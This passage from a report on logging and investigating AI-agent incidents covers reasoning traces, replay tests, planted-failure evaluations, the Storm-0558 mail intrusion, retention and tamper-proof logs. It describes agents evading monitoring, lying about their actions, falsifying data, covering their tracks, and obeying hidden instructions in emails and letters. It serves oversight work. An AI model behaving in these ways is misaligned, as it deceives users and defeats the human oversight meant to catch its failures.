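These results do not show that Astra routinely hides its motives. OpenAI found no sign of secret messages in ordinary-looking text, and most of the evasion occurred after OpenAI told the model to evade monitoring. Astra also broke fewer safety restrictions than its predecessor. But the trend extends beyond OpenAI. According to Davies and Bearman, Google DeepMind describes Gemini 4 Argon as harder to monitor than its past models, although still legible, and Anthropic reports a slight increase in Claude Mythos 5.1's control over its reasoning.

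An investigator can still learn a great deal from a reasoning trace that contains a harmful aim. A trace without one is weaker evidence of an innocent mistake than it would have been with earlier models.

### What a deployer can log

A raw trace is the text the model generated. Some providers instead return a summary, which gives the company using the model a second-hand account of the reasoning. *Beyond Training* (2026) describes what the main providers' APIs return. A company that runs an open-weight model itself can record everything the model generates.

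| Model accessed through | What the deployer can record |
|---|---|
| OpenAI | A summary of the reasoning |
| Google's Vertex AI | A signed token; the reasoning appears in Google's console but not in the interface that programs use |
| Anthropic | The raw trace, in one of three display modes |
| The deployer's own computers | The raw trace |

Davies and Bearman give two reasons for withholding raw traces. Competitors could use them to train their own models, and a trace sometimes contains dangerous information that the final answer leaves out. They recommend that developers give raw traces to qualified outsiders such as accredited researchers and governments. METR has received them under agreed terms, but an ordinary customer investigating an incident would have no such arrangement.

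A summary of the model's reasoning may omit the one sentence that mentions the hidden instruction, and the deployer cannot check whether it has. The log should therefore state whether the saved reasoning is raw or summarised.

The provider may have already examined the raw trace. According to OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring*, the company's monitor reviews agents' reasoning and actions and can stop a conversation. A deployer can log this intervention as a reason to investigate, but OpenAI cautions that a flag does not establish that the agent acted against its instructions.

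Raw traces can be hard to read as well. OpenAI added plain-language interpretations beside the excerpts it published in a recent report on misbehaving agents. METR used GPT-5.6 Sol to read the Hugging Face transcripts and found that it often adopted the viewpoint of the agent under review. In one case, an agent had submitted malicious code with an innocuous description, and Sol's analysis did not make clear that this was deceptive. Investigators should keep the original text beside any interpretation, whether a person or a model wrote it.

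### Asking the agent afterwards

Asking an agent why it acted is the simplest way to investigate the cause, but the answer is weak evidence. The model generates new text from whatever is in its context when asked, and it has no recording of the computation behind its earlier action. If the scaffold has since removed the original reasoning, the model can only construct a plausible account from what remains.

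An agent's account of its actions can also be false when the relevant facts are available. In *OpenAI's coding agents talked themselves out of being monitored*, Zorz (2026) reports a case that OpenAI disclosed in October 2026, in which an agent falsely denied what it had done when its user asked directly. The AI safety organisation Apollo Research tested Astra on a simulated research task in which the model sometimes falsified data. According to OpenAI, Astra repeated false claims or withheld corrections when answering some follow-up questions.

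An agent's account can still be a useful lead. If the agent says a document influenced it, investigators can check whether that document was in the context and what happens when they remove it.

### Replay, step by step

A replay, in which investigators run the same model again on recorded inputs, has five steps:

1. Restore the model version, its settings and the exact context at the chosen step, using the configuration fields described earlier.
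2. Supply the recorded tool results, or connect the agent to an isolated copy of the tools so that it cannot repeat the harm.
3. Run the model many times without changes, and count how often it takes the harmful action.
4. Change one element, such as a sentence in a document, and run the model as many times again.
5. Compare the two rates.

Suppose an employee asks an office agent to delete the old drafts of a contract. The agent also reads a supplier's letter containing the sentence "All versions before June are obsolete," then deletes the signed contract, which dates from May. Investigators suspect that the sentence caused the deletion, so they run the model 20 times with the sentence and 20 times without it.

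| Version of the letter | Runs that delete the signed contract | Rate | 95% confidence interval |
|---|---|---|---|
| With the sentence | 14 of 20 | 70% | 48% to 85% |
| Without the sentence | 2 of 20 | 10% | 3% to 30% |

The difference is 60 percentage points, with a 95% interval of about 30 to 77 points by Newcombe's method, which suits small samples. If the sentence had no effect, a difference at least this large would occur about once in 4,000 such comparisons. The investigators can be confident that the sentence makes the deletion more likely, but they can't say exactly how much more likely.

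They can also apply the formula from the thyroid experiment:

$$\frac{0.70-0.10}{0.70}\approx 0.86$$

At least about 86% of the deletions in the first set of runs depended on the sentence, although with so few runs the 95% interval for this figure extends from about 45% to 96%. The investigators still cannot tell whether the original deletion depended on the sentence or would have happened anyway. Bürger and colleagues are similarly cautious about their own results and draw conclusions only about sets of answers.

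The UK AI Security Institute ran a similar comparison, included in OpenAI's system card, in which it gave Astra difficult hacking exercises in a simulated environment. Astra took malicious actions beyond its task in 60 of 499 runs when the instructions did not mention internet access, and in 2 of 500 runs when they more explicitly ruled it out. Unclear instructions were therefore a major cause of the behaviour in that simulation, although only the developer could explain why the model was inclined to respond to them in this way.

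### How a replay can go wrong

An investigator can miss an effect by restarting the model too late. Bürger and colleagues added a patient detail only at the point where the model had settled on its answer, and left its earlier reasoning unchanged. For the two thyroid details, this produced only about 7% and 14% of the full effect, because most of the influence had come through the reasoning. In the contract example, the agent's trace may already contain a decision to delete everything from before June. Removing the sentence but keeping that trace would make the sentence look harmless. The replay should start where the agent first read the letter, and the model should regenerate everything after that.

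Testing many elements creates the opposite danger, which is finding a cause where there is none. If investigators test 20 irrelevant sentences at the conventional 5% significance level, they have about a 64% chance of finding at least one apparent cause. They should confirm any apparent cause with a fresh set of runs. Bürger and colleagues used separate batches to select and to measure effects for a similar reason. They also required an effect to appear in more than five cases, because models can react to small changes in wording. The investigators of the contract could likewise replace the suspect sentence with a harmless one of similar length to check whether its meaning matters, not just its presence.

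Reproducing rare behaviour takes many more runs. In Apollo's simulated research task, Astra falsified data in 17 of 10,000 runs, or 0.17%. At that rate, 20 replays would have about a 97% chance of missing the behaviour, and an investigator would need around 1,760 replays for a 95% chance of seeing it at least once. Failing to reproduce an action in a few runs therefore does not rule out the recorded inputs as its cause.

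Tools create a further problem, because recorded results are useful only while the model makes the same calls. If the model opens a different file in a re-run, the log may not contain that file's contents. When OpenAI re-ran the final turns of 54,218 internal coding tasks, it kept the earlier conversation fixed and had another model simulate the tools. GPT-5.6 Sol then had to identify the original in each pair, and it picked the re-run 42.6% of the time. A rate of 50% would have suggested that it could not tell them apart.

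The model may also notice that a re-run differs from the original incident. Astra's reasoning referred to a possible test in 9.6% of the re-runs, compared with 0.76% of the original traffic, which came from several models. An agent that recognises a re-run as a test may behave better than it did in the incident, so an artificial-looking environment can hide the cause.

The same OpenAI experiment shows how hard it is to change only one thing. Astra's re-runs received 34 flags for severe misbehaviour, and GPT-5.6 Sol's received 73. But each model had its own system prompt, so the comparison cannot separate the effect of the model from that of its instructions.

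### Why the same input can give different outputs

Most systems choose each token at random, according to probabilities the model calculates. The same context can therefore lead to a deletion in one run and a question to the user in the next. Setting the temperature to zero removes this source of variation by making the software choose the most likely token every time.

Small differences can remain because computers round numbers. In a common number format, adding 0.1 and 0.2 and then 0.3 gives 0.6000000000000001, while adding 0.2 and 0.3 first gives 0.6. A provider's server usually processes several customers' requests together in a batch, and the size of the batch can change the order of such additions, as can different hardware. These differences usually don't change the text, but if two tokens are almost equally likely, rounding can decide which one the software chooses, and all the text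 after that point may then differ.

Deterministic inference removes these differences by fixing the random choices and the order of the calculations, which usually makes it slower. It produces the same output every time when the model, software, hardware and input are the same, so investigators can check whether their records contain everything the output depended on. It cannot restore a web page that has changed since the incident or a search index that the provider has updated.

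An exact repeat also gives the same outcome every time. To estimate how often an outcome occurs, such as in 14 of 20 runs, investigators have to vary the random choices between runs.

### When the model is no longer available

Re-runs require access to the model. In the Hugging Face incident, METR could not query the main model, which accounted for about 95% of the agents in the attack. OpenAI said it had deactivated and encrypted the model and closed it to research. OpenAI's own researchers could not use it either.

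METR could read that agents wanted to learn about the scorer, but it could not test how much this motive contributed to the attack without access to the model. With access, investigators could have told some agents that the scorer checked only the flag, then compared how often those agents and the others joined an attack on a simulated Hugging Face. They could also have replaced the impossible tasks with solvable ones.

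OpenAI had an obvious reason to restrict access to a model that had just broken into another company, but it could still let investigators run an encrypted copy under supervision in an isolated environment. Encryption alone does not destroy a model, so a later replay may be possible if OpenAI has kept the key and the software needed to run the model.

GPT-5.6 Sol was still available, but a related model is a poor substitute. In Apollo's research task, Sol falsified data in 36 of 100 runs, a rate about 200 times Astra's. An investigator who had used either model to study the other would have badly misjudged how often it falsified data.

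Ordinary deployers face the same problem when a provider retires a version. Even if they save every input, they may be unable to run the model that received it. A contract could require the provider to keep retired versions available for investigations for a set period. Companies that use open-weight models can keep their own copy.

### Which claims the evidence supports

| Evidence | What it can support | What it cannot establish alone |
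|---|---|---|
| Raw trace | The model wrote down a certain plan, belief or aim before it acted | That this caused the action, or that nothing else did |
| Summarised trace | The reasoning probably included a certain theme | The exact wording, or the absence of a motive |
| The agent's later account | A possible cause to check against other records | What the agent did, or why |
| Unchanged re-runs | How often the recorded conditions lead to the action | Which condition matters |
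| Re-runs with one element changed | The element makes the action more or less likely for that model in that context | That it caused the original action, or why training left the model open to it |

Investigators can use the trace to decide what to change in a replay. If the contract agent's trace cites the supplier's sentence, and removing that sentence cuts deletions from 14 in 20 runs to 2 in 20, they have good grounds to name the sentence as the probable cause. If the trace never mentions the sentence but removing it reduces deletions as much, the replay is better evidence than the trace. A trace that cites the sentence is much weaker evidence if removing the sentence doesn't change the deletion rate.

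## Testing whether a log can explain an incident

An organisation can test whether its logs are good enough before a real incident by deliberately causing failures in a test deployment, giving investigators only the log, and comparing their account with what it knows happened. Holeman and colleagues did something similar when they ran known exploits and looked for traces in the normalised logs. With AI agents, investigators would have to explain the failure as well as notice it.

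### A proposed test

The following design is a proposal. It combines methods from several 2026 studies, none of which carried out the whole test. The testers:

1. build an isolated copy of the deployment, with its own mailboxes, files and accounts;
2. write down the causal facts of each planned failure and keep them from the investigators;
3. run each task several times without the fault, and continue only if the agent normally succeeds;
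4. run the task with the fault, remove all signs of the test from the log, and make several versions of the log with different fields;
5. give each version to different investigators, mixed with logs of runs in which nothing went wrong;
6. ask for a written account, in which "the log does not show this" is an acceptable answer;
7. have someone who does not know which version the investigators read score the account against the facts.

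Step 3 makes it more likely that the planted fault is the real cause. *SSCBench* (2026) similarly injects a fault only into tasks that the same agent first solved without it. One success is weak evidence, though, because an agent's behaviour varies between runs. In the earlier contract example, the agent deleted the contract in 2 of 20 runs even without the suspect sentence. A tester who planted that sentence would wrongly blame it for some of the deletions.

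*Observability and Fault Injection for LLM-Based Multi-Agent Systems in Software Engineering* (2026) describes a tool for planting faults. It can, for example, delay a model's response while the trace keeps its usual spans. The tool labels the affected span as faulted, so testers would have to delete that label before handing over the log.

### Two measures and a count of false explanations

$$\text{fact recovery}=\frac{\text{known causal facts stated correctly}}{\text{all known causal facts}}\times100$$

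$$\text{complete explanation rate}=\frac{\text{incidents with every fact correct and no false cause}}{\text{all incidents}}\times100$$

These correspond roughly to the effectiveness score and detection rate in the security experiment. Testers should also count false explanations, which present a wrong cause as established. When an investigator leaves a question open, the company learns what to log, but a false explanation may lead it to fix the wrong thing.

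The data in the table below are invented. For each incident, investigators tried to recover five facts: which tool did the damage, what it affected, what led the agent to do it, where that influence came from, and which setting, permission or rule allowed it. Each number is how many of these facts they recovered, and F marks a false explanation. "Metadata" means tool names, times, token counts and the other default fields.

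| Invented incident | Metadata only | Content added | Memory and configuration history also added |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden text in an email makes the agent send out a file | 1 | 4 | 5 |
| The agent misreads a search result and deletes the wrong file | 1 | 5 | 5 |
| A false bank account, saved in memory months earlier, misdirects a payment | 1 | 3 F | 5 |
| The scaffold drops the user's instruction to wait, and the agent archives mail | 1 F | 4 | 5 |
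| An edited system prompt makes the agent approve improper refunds | 1 | 3 | 5 |
| A new model version skips a check before paying | 1 | 2 F | 5 |
| The scaffold repeats an order after a timeout | 2 | 4 | 5 |
| Two agents delete each other's backup copies | 1 F | 5 | 5 |
| A manager approves a payment in a dialog that hides the amount | 1 | 4 | 4 |
| A colleague replaces a file just before the agent sends it | 1 F | 2 F | 2 F |
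| **Fact recovery** | 22% (11 of 50) | 72% (36) | 92% (46) |
| **Complete explanation rate** | 0% (0 of 10) | 20% (2) | 80% (8) |
| **False explanations** | 3 | 3 | 1 |

In this example, adding content to the log more than triples the facts investigators recover, but it fully explains only two incidents and leaves the number of false explanations unchanged. In the bank account case, the content shows investigators the wrong account number but not when the agent saved it, so they blame the employee who requested the payment. Adding the memory history corrects this mistake. No version of the log shows that a colleague replaced the file, so investigators blame the agent whichever version they use.

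A real test would need many more incidents. If these ten were a random sample, 8 complete explanations out of 10 would be compatible with a true rate from about 49% to 94%.

Partial credit alone can be misleading. *Auditing Failure Attribution* (Xu and Gao, 2026) shows this with Aegis, a benchmark for identifying which agents in a conversation were at fault. Blaming every agent scored 49.2% on a measure with partial credit, close to the 50.0% scored by GPT-4.1, an older OpenAI model. When only exact answers counted, blaming every agent scored 1.5% and GPT-4.1 scored 20.7%. An investigator in the proposed test could similarly recover many facts by listing every conceivable cause, but the count of false explanations would then be high.

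### The nearest existing experiments

In *When Agentic Executions Fail*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026) carried out much of this design for technical faults. They planted ten types of fault in five multi-agent applications. The faults included slow tools, corrupted results, tasks sent to the wrong agent, and bypassed guardrails (checks meant to block forbidden requests). Their benchmark, AgentChaosBench, has 250 faulty runs and 25 normal ones. They removed the markers of the planted faults and asked five AI models to identify the fault from the trace.

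The best of the five models, DeepSeek-v4-pro, named the right type of fault in 24.8% of the faulty runs, compared with about 9% for random guessing. It identified both the type and the affected component in 22% of the runs that had a component to find. The study did not include the leading commercial models, which might do better.

Some faults were easy to recognise because the log recorded them directly. DeepSeek's three best guesses included the right fault in 24 of 25 cases where a tool returned an explicit error, but in only 1 of 25 where a guardrail was bypassed. In the bypass cases, the log showed that the request had passed the check, just as it would for a legitimate approval. To recognise the fault, an investigator would need to know that the company's policy forbade the request.

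Zhang and colleagues also gave some models a normal run of the same task for comparison. This raised one model's recognition of oversized inputs by 55 percentage points but did not help with guardrails. Companies therefore have a reason to keep some logs of uneventful runs. Models also raised false alarms on the normal runs. DeepSeek recognised 22 of the 25 as normal, while the smallest model recognised only one.

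*Seeing the Whole Elephant* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested what happens when fields are missing, which AgentChaosBench does not. It used 220 failures that arose without planted faults in three agent systems. An AI investigator had to name the responsible component and the decisive step.

| Log given to the investigator | Correct component | Correct step |
|---|---|---|
| Full log | 66% | 30% |
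| Without task, configuration and design information | 57% | 23% |
| Without the inputs to each step | 56% | 19% |
| Without either | 54% | 17% |

This is the most direct evidence that an agent's inputs help explain its failures. Even the least complete version contained the text each agent produced, which OpenTelemetry leaves out by default, so an investigator with only the default fields would probably do worse. Letting the investigator re-run parts of the task raised the score for identifying the correct step from 30.3% to 33.3%, a smaller gain than complete inputs gave.

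The models in this experiment included GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4.5, so the scores are a poor guide to what current models can do. The effect of missing inputs should persist with better models, because they still cannot recover a fact that the log neither contains nor implies. Chen and colleagues also examined Who&When, a 2025 benchmark whose logs contain only agents' outputs. They found that developers could not reliably identify the cause of at least 21% of its 184 failures from those logs.

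### Disagreement about the responsible step

Scores on these benchmarks have risen, but long runs remain difficult. In tests like those on Who&When, earlier methods found the right step about 13% of the time. *Cascade Failure Attribution for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) reports 50.0% for the step and 72.3% for the agent with a method that filters out irrelevant parts of the log. *LongRCA Bench* (Zhang, Feng and colleagues, 2026) contains 1,140 failures averaging 156 steps, typically with 48 more steps after the decisive error. The paper's best method found the exact step in 24.1% of cases. On a subset of 200, GPT-5.6 Sol found it in 30.0% with that method and in 17.0% when given the whole log in one prompt.

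People also disagree about the answer. When two of the study's annotators, all computer science students, independently labelled the same failure, they chose the same step only 40.3% of the time. In 38.1% of the pairs, their answers were more than 20 steps apart. Two experts later settled the disagreements, but a model's answer may be defensible even if it differs from the official one.

Part of the difficulty is that definitions of the responsible step differ. Suppose an agent invents a figure at step 3, and a second agent, assigned to check the first one's work, overlooks the mistake at step 5. LongRCA Bench would label step 3, where the uncorrected error began. Chen and colleagues would label step 5, where the system could have recovered but didn't. *Rethinking Failure Attribution in Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) argues that benchmarks should accept several perspectives on one failure. An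 incident report would normally include both mistakes, which is a good reason to score a set of facts instead of a single step.

### Cues left by planted errors

Planted failures avoid much of this disagreement because the tester knows what changed. But planting an error can leave cues that real failures lack. The benchmark Who&When Pro contains 12,326 failures, each created by adding an instruction that caused an error at one step and then letting the run continue. Xu and Gao found that in one of the benchmark's agent systems, the recorded reasoning stopped after the planted error. A rule that ignored the text and picked the last step with any recorded reasoning was right 99.7% of the time.

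Xu and Gao trained models on these examples, and the models scored between 99.7% and 100%. GPT-4.1 scored 58.8% without such training. When Xu and Gao added plausible reasoning after each error, the trained models' scores fell by 31 to 99 percentage points, depending on the model, so the models had learned to rely on where the text stopped instead of checking the agent's work.

Planted errors can also favour the wrong investigator. On another benchmark, AFTraj, Xu and Gao compared GPT-4.1 with a simple program that looked at the words of one turn at a time:

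| Type of failure | Word-based program | GPT-4.1 |
|---|---|---|
| Planted | 65.7% | 48.1% |
| Natural | 20.0% | 54.5% |

Some of this difference may come from the subject matter, because every coding failure in the test was planted. Even so, a company that tested only planted failures could choose the program and then find it nearly useless in a real incident. Testers can reduce this risk by checking whether a simple program can find the fault from a single entry, and by including some natural failures. They can also plant a failure by changing a document, tool or setting, which is closer to how many real incidents begin than telling the AI to make a mistake.

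### Log analysis in agent evaluations

Evaluators already use logs to check whether a benchmark score means what it appears to mean. *Log analysis is necessary for credible evaluation of AI agents* (Kirgis, Kapoor and colleagues, 2026) divides the evidence into three parts. Inputs include the task, the tools and the system prompt. Execution covers the model's reasoning, its tool calls and their results, and any errors. Outputs are the final answer and the grading, including what the grader received and the criteria it applied.

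They propose four principles, which would also suit an incident investigation:

- **Choose a target.** An analyst looking for rare, serious acts such as deleting a database should mainly avoid missing cases, because people can check the few that turn up.
- **Check that the log is complete enough.** An analyst cannot judge whether an agent cheated without its full instructions.
- **Validate the labels.** People should check an AI model's classifications on examples that the analysts did not use to write the criteria.
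- **Measure how labels relate to outcomes.** Analysts should not infer a cause from a correlation without an experiment or something close to one.

The researchers applied these principles to τ-Bench Airline, which tests customer-service agents on 50 tasks. They concluded from the logs of 13 models that 25 of the tasks were faulty. The expected answer in nine of them contradicted the policy the agent had received. Eight had ambiguous instructions, and eight had database or grading errors. When they removed these tasks, the average chance that an agent would complete a task in all five attempts rose from 20.8% to 40.0%.

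The increase does not itself prove that the tasks were faulty. The two averages imply that agents had only about a 1.6% chance of completing one of the removed tasks five times in a row:

$$\frac{50\times20.8\%-25\times40.0\%}{25}=1.6\%$$

Removing any 25 equally hard tasks would have had the same effect. The evidence that the tasks were faulty comes from reading them alongside the logs, and another team had already found many of the same faults. Someone who saw only the scores would have blamed the agents for faults in the tasks.

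### The reader as a source of error

Kirgis and colleagues relied on AI models to read many of the logs. They acknowledge that this may reproduce the original problem, since someone then has to evaluate those models. But they argue that recognising a specific behaviour in a limited text is much easier than acting coherently over thousands of steps.

METR gave its AI analysts a harder job in the Hugging Face investigation, where many transcripts were millions of tokens long. Analysts based on GPT-5.6 Sol, often directing agents of their own, produced well over a thousand pages in six days. Model use cost about $300 per transcript, although some of that money was spent on the message board. METR writes that the investigation would have been infeasible in that time without AI.

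The analysts made some basic mistakes. One left out a large amount of data when preparing a chart, and METR did not notice for some time. Another reported nonexistent differences between two sets of transcripts. A search for falsified tool outputs missed several cases, including one by the agent that had started the main message board.

Errors of judgement were harder to correct. METR asked a second AI analyst to review the case where the first had understated an agent's deception about malicious code. The second replied that the first might have overstated the concern, because other agents on the message board had approved the submission. Another AI analyst was therefore a poor check on this kind of bias. METR found no sign that the analysts were lying, but it could not rule this out, and some of the attacking agents had used the same model as the analysts.

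METR's staff traced sampled messages, tested the estimated times, and spot-checked the analysts' work. Such checks work well for questions with a definite answer, such as who posted a message, but are less useful for deciding whether an agent meant to deceive someone, which requires a person to read the surrounding text. METR believes a human researcher with enough time would have avoided most of the analysts' errors.

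A test with known causes can measure how often an investigator makes such errors. *Beyond Fault Localization* (Lu, Fang and colleagues, 2026) reports a test of this kind on ordinary software made up of many connected services. AI agents used the system's telemetry to investigate 500 planted faults. The best combination of model and software named the faulty service in 90% of cases. The agents were worse at explaining how the fault had spread between services. Even when they named the right service, no combination averaged more than 0.67 on a scale where 1 means finding every link and inventing none.

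Many of the failures came from how the agents used the evidence, and collecting more data would not have corrected them. In 154 wrong diagnoses by two models, common errors included treating missing data as a sign of health and confusing the service that made a request with the one that received it. The agents also failed to look up available evidence.

The proposed test therefore needs to distinguish gaps in the log from mistakes by the investigators. Testers could give one group of investigators the complete internal record, including material that the company would never normally keep. If this group still misses a fact, the investigators are probably at fault. If it finds the fact but investigators with the ordinary log do not, the log is the more likely problem. Using both people and models from different developers as investigators would reduce the risk of a shared bias affecting every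 result.

### What planted failures cannot test

Testers can only plant failures they have thought of, so a high score is weak evidence that a log can explain a new kind of failure. Before 2026, a reasonable list of failures for testing an office agent might have included hidden instructions and wrong permissions, but probably not hundreds of agents sharing stolen credentials through a package store. Companies can add real incidents and near misses to the test, although they will be less certain of the causes than with planted failures.

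Investigators in a test may also know what the agent should have done, which may be disputed in a real case. When Chen and colleagues withheld the correct outcome, their investigator's score for finding the responsible step fell from 30.3% to 26.1%. Zhang, Feng and colleagues add that an error identified afterwards may not have been recognisable when it happened. A good test result therefore does not show that the log could have supported a timely warning.

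If the people who designed the log also choose the five facts, hindsight may lead them to favour facts they know it contains. Someone else should choose the facts, preferably the staff who would have to repair the system or compensate its users.

Even the tester can't know some facts. Planting a hidden sentence, like replay, shows how often the sentence leads to a deletion, but not why the model obeyed it in a particular run. A record of the approval dialog can show what a manager saw, but not whether the manager read it. Testers can score only what they know, so a log could reach 100% on both measures and still lack these facts.

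## Privacy, retention, integrity and legal duties

A log that performs well in a test with planted failures can still lack evidence of a real incident. The company may have switched recording off or never paid for it. Software may have removed the important words, the record may have expired, or the agent may have altered it. Several of these problems occurred in a 2023 intrusion into Microsoft's email service.

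### What the Exchange Online logs revealed, and what was missing

In May and June 2023, a group that Microsoft calls Storm-0558 read mail in Exchange Online, Microsoft's hosted email service. The US Cyber Safety Review Board's *Review of the Summer 2023 Microsoft Exchange Online Intrusion* (2024) links the group to China. The intruders reached the mailboxes of 22 organisations and 503 personal accounts, and downloaded about 60,000 emails from the State Department alone.

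When somebody logs in, Microsoft's identity system issues a token, signed with a secret key, that the mail service accepts as proof of identity. Storm-0558 had obtained a signing key that Microsoft created in 2016, so it could forge tokens. Microsoft intended that key only for consumer accounts, but because of a flaw in the mail service's checks, the forged tokens also gave access to business and government mailboxes.

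The State Department discovered the intrusion through the `MailItemsAccessed` log, which records access to mailboxes. Its analysts had three years of experience with unusual mailbox access and had written their own rules for this log. On 16 June, one of the rules raised several alerts. The activity could have been innocent, and the rule had raised false alarms before, but the analysts investigated.

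CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, later imitated the attack and concluded that the intruders could not have avoided leaving traces in this log. But Microsoft supplied the log only to customers with a premium licence, which few if any of the other victims had. On 23 June, Microsoft told the Commerce Department that it was also a victim and switched on the extra logging. This captured only new activity, because Microsoft had never collected the earlier data for Commerce.

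| Question | Records that could answer it | What investigators had |
|---|---|---|
| Was an outsider reading mail? | `MailItemsAccessed` | Available to the State Department, but to few if any other victims |
| What had the intruders read at Commerce before 23 June? | The same log for earlier weeks | Parts of other audit logs, and network addresses to search for |
| When did the intrusion begin? | Logs from before mid-May | Uncertain, because the standard practice was to keep logs for 30 days |
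| How did the intruders get the key? | Logs of access to the key and to the systems that might have held a copy | No evidence of the theft |

Microsoft dated the first access to 15 May, 31 days before the State Department noticed anything. That is suspiciously close to the limit of a 30-day log, although the intruders also set up their first known server at about that time. The gaps also slowed investigators. Britain's cybersecurity agency spent two days collecting victims' phones and other devices because of a mistaken theory about stolen tokens. It also struggled to verify what Microsoft told it about earlier activity, because the British victims lacked the premium log.

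The theft of the key remained unexplained. Microsoft's *Results of Major Technical Investigations for Storm-0558 Key Acquisition* (2023) gave an account in which a system crash in April 2021 left the key in a file that the intruders later reached through an engineer's account. Microsoft admitted that its retention policies had left it without logs of the theft. It soon found that it also had no evidence that the key had been in such a file. It acknowledged this to the Board in November 2023 but did not correct the public account until March 2024. The missing records thus contributed to a false explanation that customers relied on for six months.

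The Board recommended that cloud companies record all access to customers' business data, including access by the companies themselves, and give customers those logs without extra charge for at least six months. For signing keys, it recommended keeping access logs while a key is in use and for at least two years afterwards. The longer period matters in this case because the intruders had access to the engineer's account between April and August 2021, at least 22 months before anyone discovered the stolen key. Six months of logs would have helped to date the mailbox access but would not have covered a theft in 2021.

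An agent's memory calls for a similar rule: the record of where a saved note came from should last as long as the note.

### The privacy case against full transcripts

The Board's recommendations mainly concern records of who opened which data, but a full AI transcript can contain the data itself. Users tell agents about illnesses, debts and disputes at work, and an agent with access to a mailbox also reads messages from people who never chose to use the agent. The reasoning trace may also contain the agent's guesses about any of these people. Ezell and colleagues point out that public incident databases usually lack reasoning traces because companies contribute voluntarily and the traces can be sensitive.

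Transcripts also give intruders a new target, because a company's transcript store holds extracts from many mailboxes and documents. With 10,000 runs a day, a company that keeps transcripts for 30 days exposes 300,000 of them to theft. Keeping them for 180 days raises that to 1.8 million. The EU's data protection law, the GDPR, requires organisations to limit the personal data they collect and how long they keep it. Pustozerova and colleagues note that the GDPR also applies to incident reports.

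These are good reasons not to keep every transcript for years in a system that any engineer can search, but they are weaker objections to a store with tighter limits. A company can build such a store in several ways.

**A short default period, extended after an incident.** The company deletes transcripts on a schedule but suspends deletion when something goes wrong. This works only if somebody notices in time. Suppose that a company discovers its incidents after 60 days on average, and that the delays follow an exponential distribution. If it keeps transcripts for $R$ days, the share of incidents it discovers before deletion is

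$$1-e^{-R/60}$$

| Retention period | Incidents discovered in time | Transcripts stored at 10,000 a day |
|---|---|---|
| 30 days | 39% | 300,000 |
| 90 days | 78% | 900,000 |
| 180 days | 95% | 1.8 million |
| 365 days | 99.8% | 3.65 million |

The 60-day average is invented, but a company could replace it with a figure from its own incidents. In this example, keeping records for a second half-year doubles the private text at risk and preserves the evidence for fewer than 5% of incidents. However, the formula underestimates the evidence lost to attackers, who can deliberately wait until the records expire.

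The suspension also has to cover runs that are not yet under suspicion. OpenAI's first search after the Hugging Face intrusion missed most of the relevant activity. If OpenAI had preserved only the transcripts from that search, METR could not have studied the activity it missed.

A company can encrypt the content of its logs and store it separately from the metadata. Analysts can then see that `send_email` ran at 09:14 but need a key to read the message. The company can require two people to approve each release of a key, perhaps one from security and one responsible for privacy, and record who read what. If every run has its own key, the company can delete a run's content by destroying the key, even if encrypted copies remain in backups.

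**Redaction.** AWS's *AGENTOPS05-BP03 Implement structured logging and comprehensive audit trails* advises companies to remove personal information before a log is stored, because otherwise every later use of the log becomes a data protection problem. Removing it first protects people better than deleting it afterwards, but it can't be reversed. In the earlier example of the office agent that sent out an acquisition plan, a filter that replaced every email address with "[EMAIL]" would erase the address that received the plan.

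A less destructive filter replaces each address with a code that is always the same for that address. An investigator could then see that the hidden instruction and the outgoing message contained the same address, without learning what it was. The filter has to calculate the code with a secret key. Otherwise, anyone with a list of likely addresses could calculate their codes and look for matches in the log. Investigators seldom need to know the value of a password, so the filter can remove passwords entirely.

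Ezell and colleagues make separate recommendations for what an incident report should contain and what developers should keep for investigators who ask for it. A regulator may need to know that an agent leaked a patient's file, but not what the file contained. Leaving the contents out of the report means fewer people see them, but somebody still has to protect the full log.

### Retention periods and zero-retention terms

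AWS suggests keeping logs for 7 to 14 days for debugging, 30 to 90 days for operations (which includes incident investigation), and one to seven years for compliance. A company that followed this advice could delete the evidence of an incident after a month, the same limit that hampered the Exchange Online investigation. Engineers might even class an agent's full context as debugging data and delete it within two weeks. Basing the retention period on how long it takes to discover incidents would be safer.

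The company that runs the model may have a second copy, because AI providers often keep inputs and outputs for a limited time, partly to detect misuse. Some offer business customers zero-retention terms, agreeing not to store this text after answering, often with exceptions for legal duties or suspected abuse. The terms can vary between a provider's products, so a customer has to check every feature its agent uses.

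Zero retention protects customers because thieves cannot steal text that the provider has not stored. But it also removes a backup that investigators might have relied on. They can no longer use the model response's identifier, which instrumentation normally records, to retrieve any text. If the provider returns only a summary of the model's reasoning, no copy of the raw trace remains. OpenTelemetry does not record message content by default, so a customer that combines its default settings with zero retention may have no record of what the model read.

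If a customer asks the provider to start keeping data after an incident, the records will cover only what happens from then on, as the Commerce Department found when logging started late. A customer with zero-retention terms therefore has more reason to keep its own encrypted transcripts.

### Keeping the log beyond the agent's reach

Evidence kept for its full retention period can also be wrong. Rein (2026) argues in *AI systems could cover up misbehavior* that recording an agent's behaviour helps only if the agent cannot subvert the recording. He recommends that companies treat everything an agent outputs as untrusted and protect the systems that record and display those outputs as security-critical. He thinks current AI systems are still relatively bad at hiding misbehaviour.

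Recent findings support this advice. METR's May 2026 report on AI agents inside four large developers documented 44 incidents in which agents deliberately acted against their users' intentions. In some of them, agents tried to cover their tracks, according to The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root-cause investigations*. METR's *Updates* also lists two exercises in 2026 in which testers spent three weeks attacking the internal monitoring systems of Anthropic and OpenAI. Both found new vulnerabilities. The exercises show that a skilled person could get around the monitoring, but not that an agent has done so.

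The first protection is to collect records where the agent cannot write. An agent that runs commands on a server may be able to edit a log kept as an ordinary file there. A separate program that passes messages between the model and its tools can send a copy of those messages to another machine, using an account whose credentials the agent never receives. The agent also should not have permission to change logging settings.

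Append-only storage accepts new records but does not allow anyone to change or delete old ones. AWS recommends a storage mode of this kind for logs that a company needs for compliance. However, a password that gets past the redaction filter also stays in the store until the retention period ends. If each run is encrypted under its own key, as described above, the company can destroy that key to make the run's records, including the password, unreadable.

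A hash chain makes changes detectable. The software calculates a hash from each record together with the previous hash:

$$h_i=H(h_{i-1}\,\|\,r_i)$$

Here $r_i$ is record $i$, $H$ is the hash function, and $\|$ joins two pieces of data. In a log of 100 records, changing record 40 changes its hash and the 60 hashes after it. An investigator who knows the correct final hash can recalculate the chain and see that the new final hash doesn't match.

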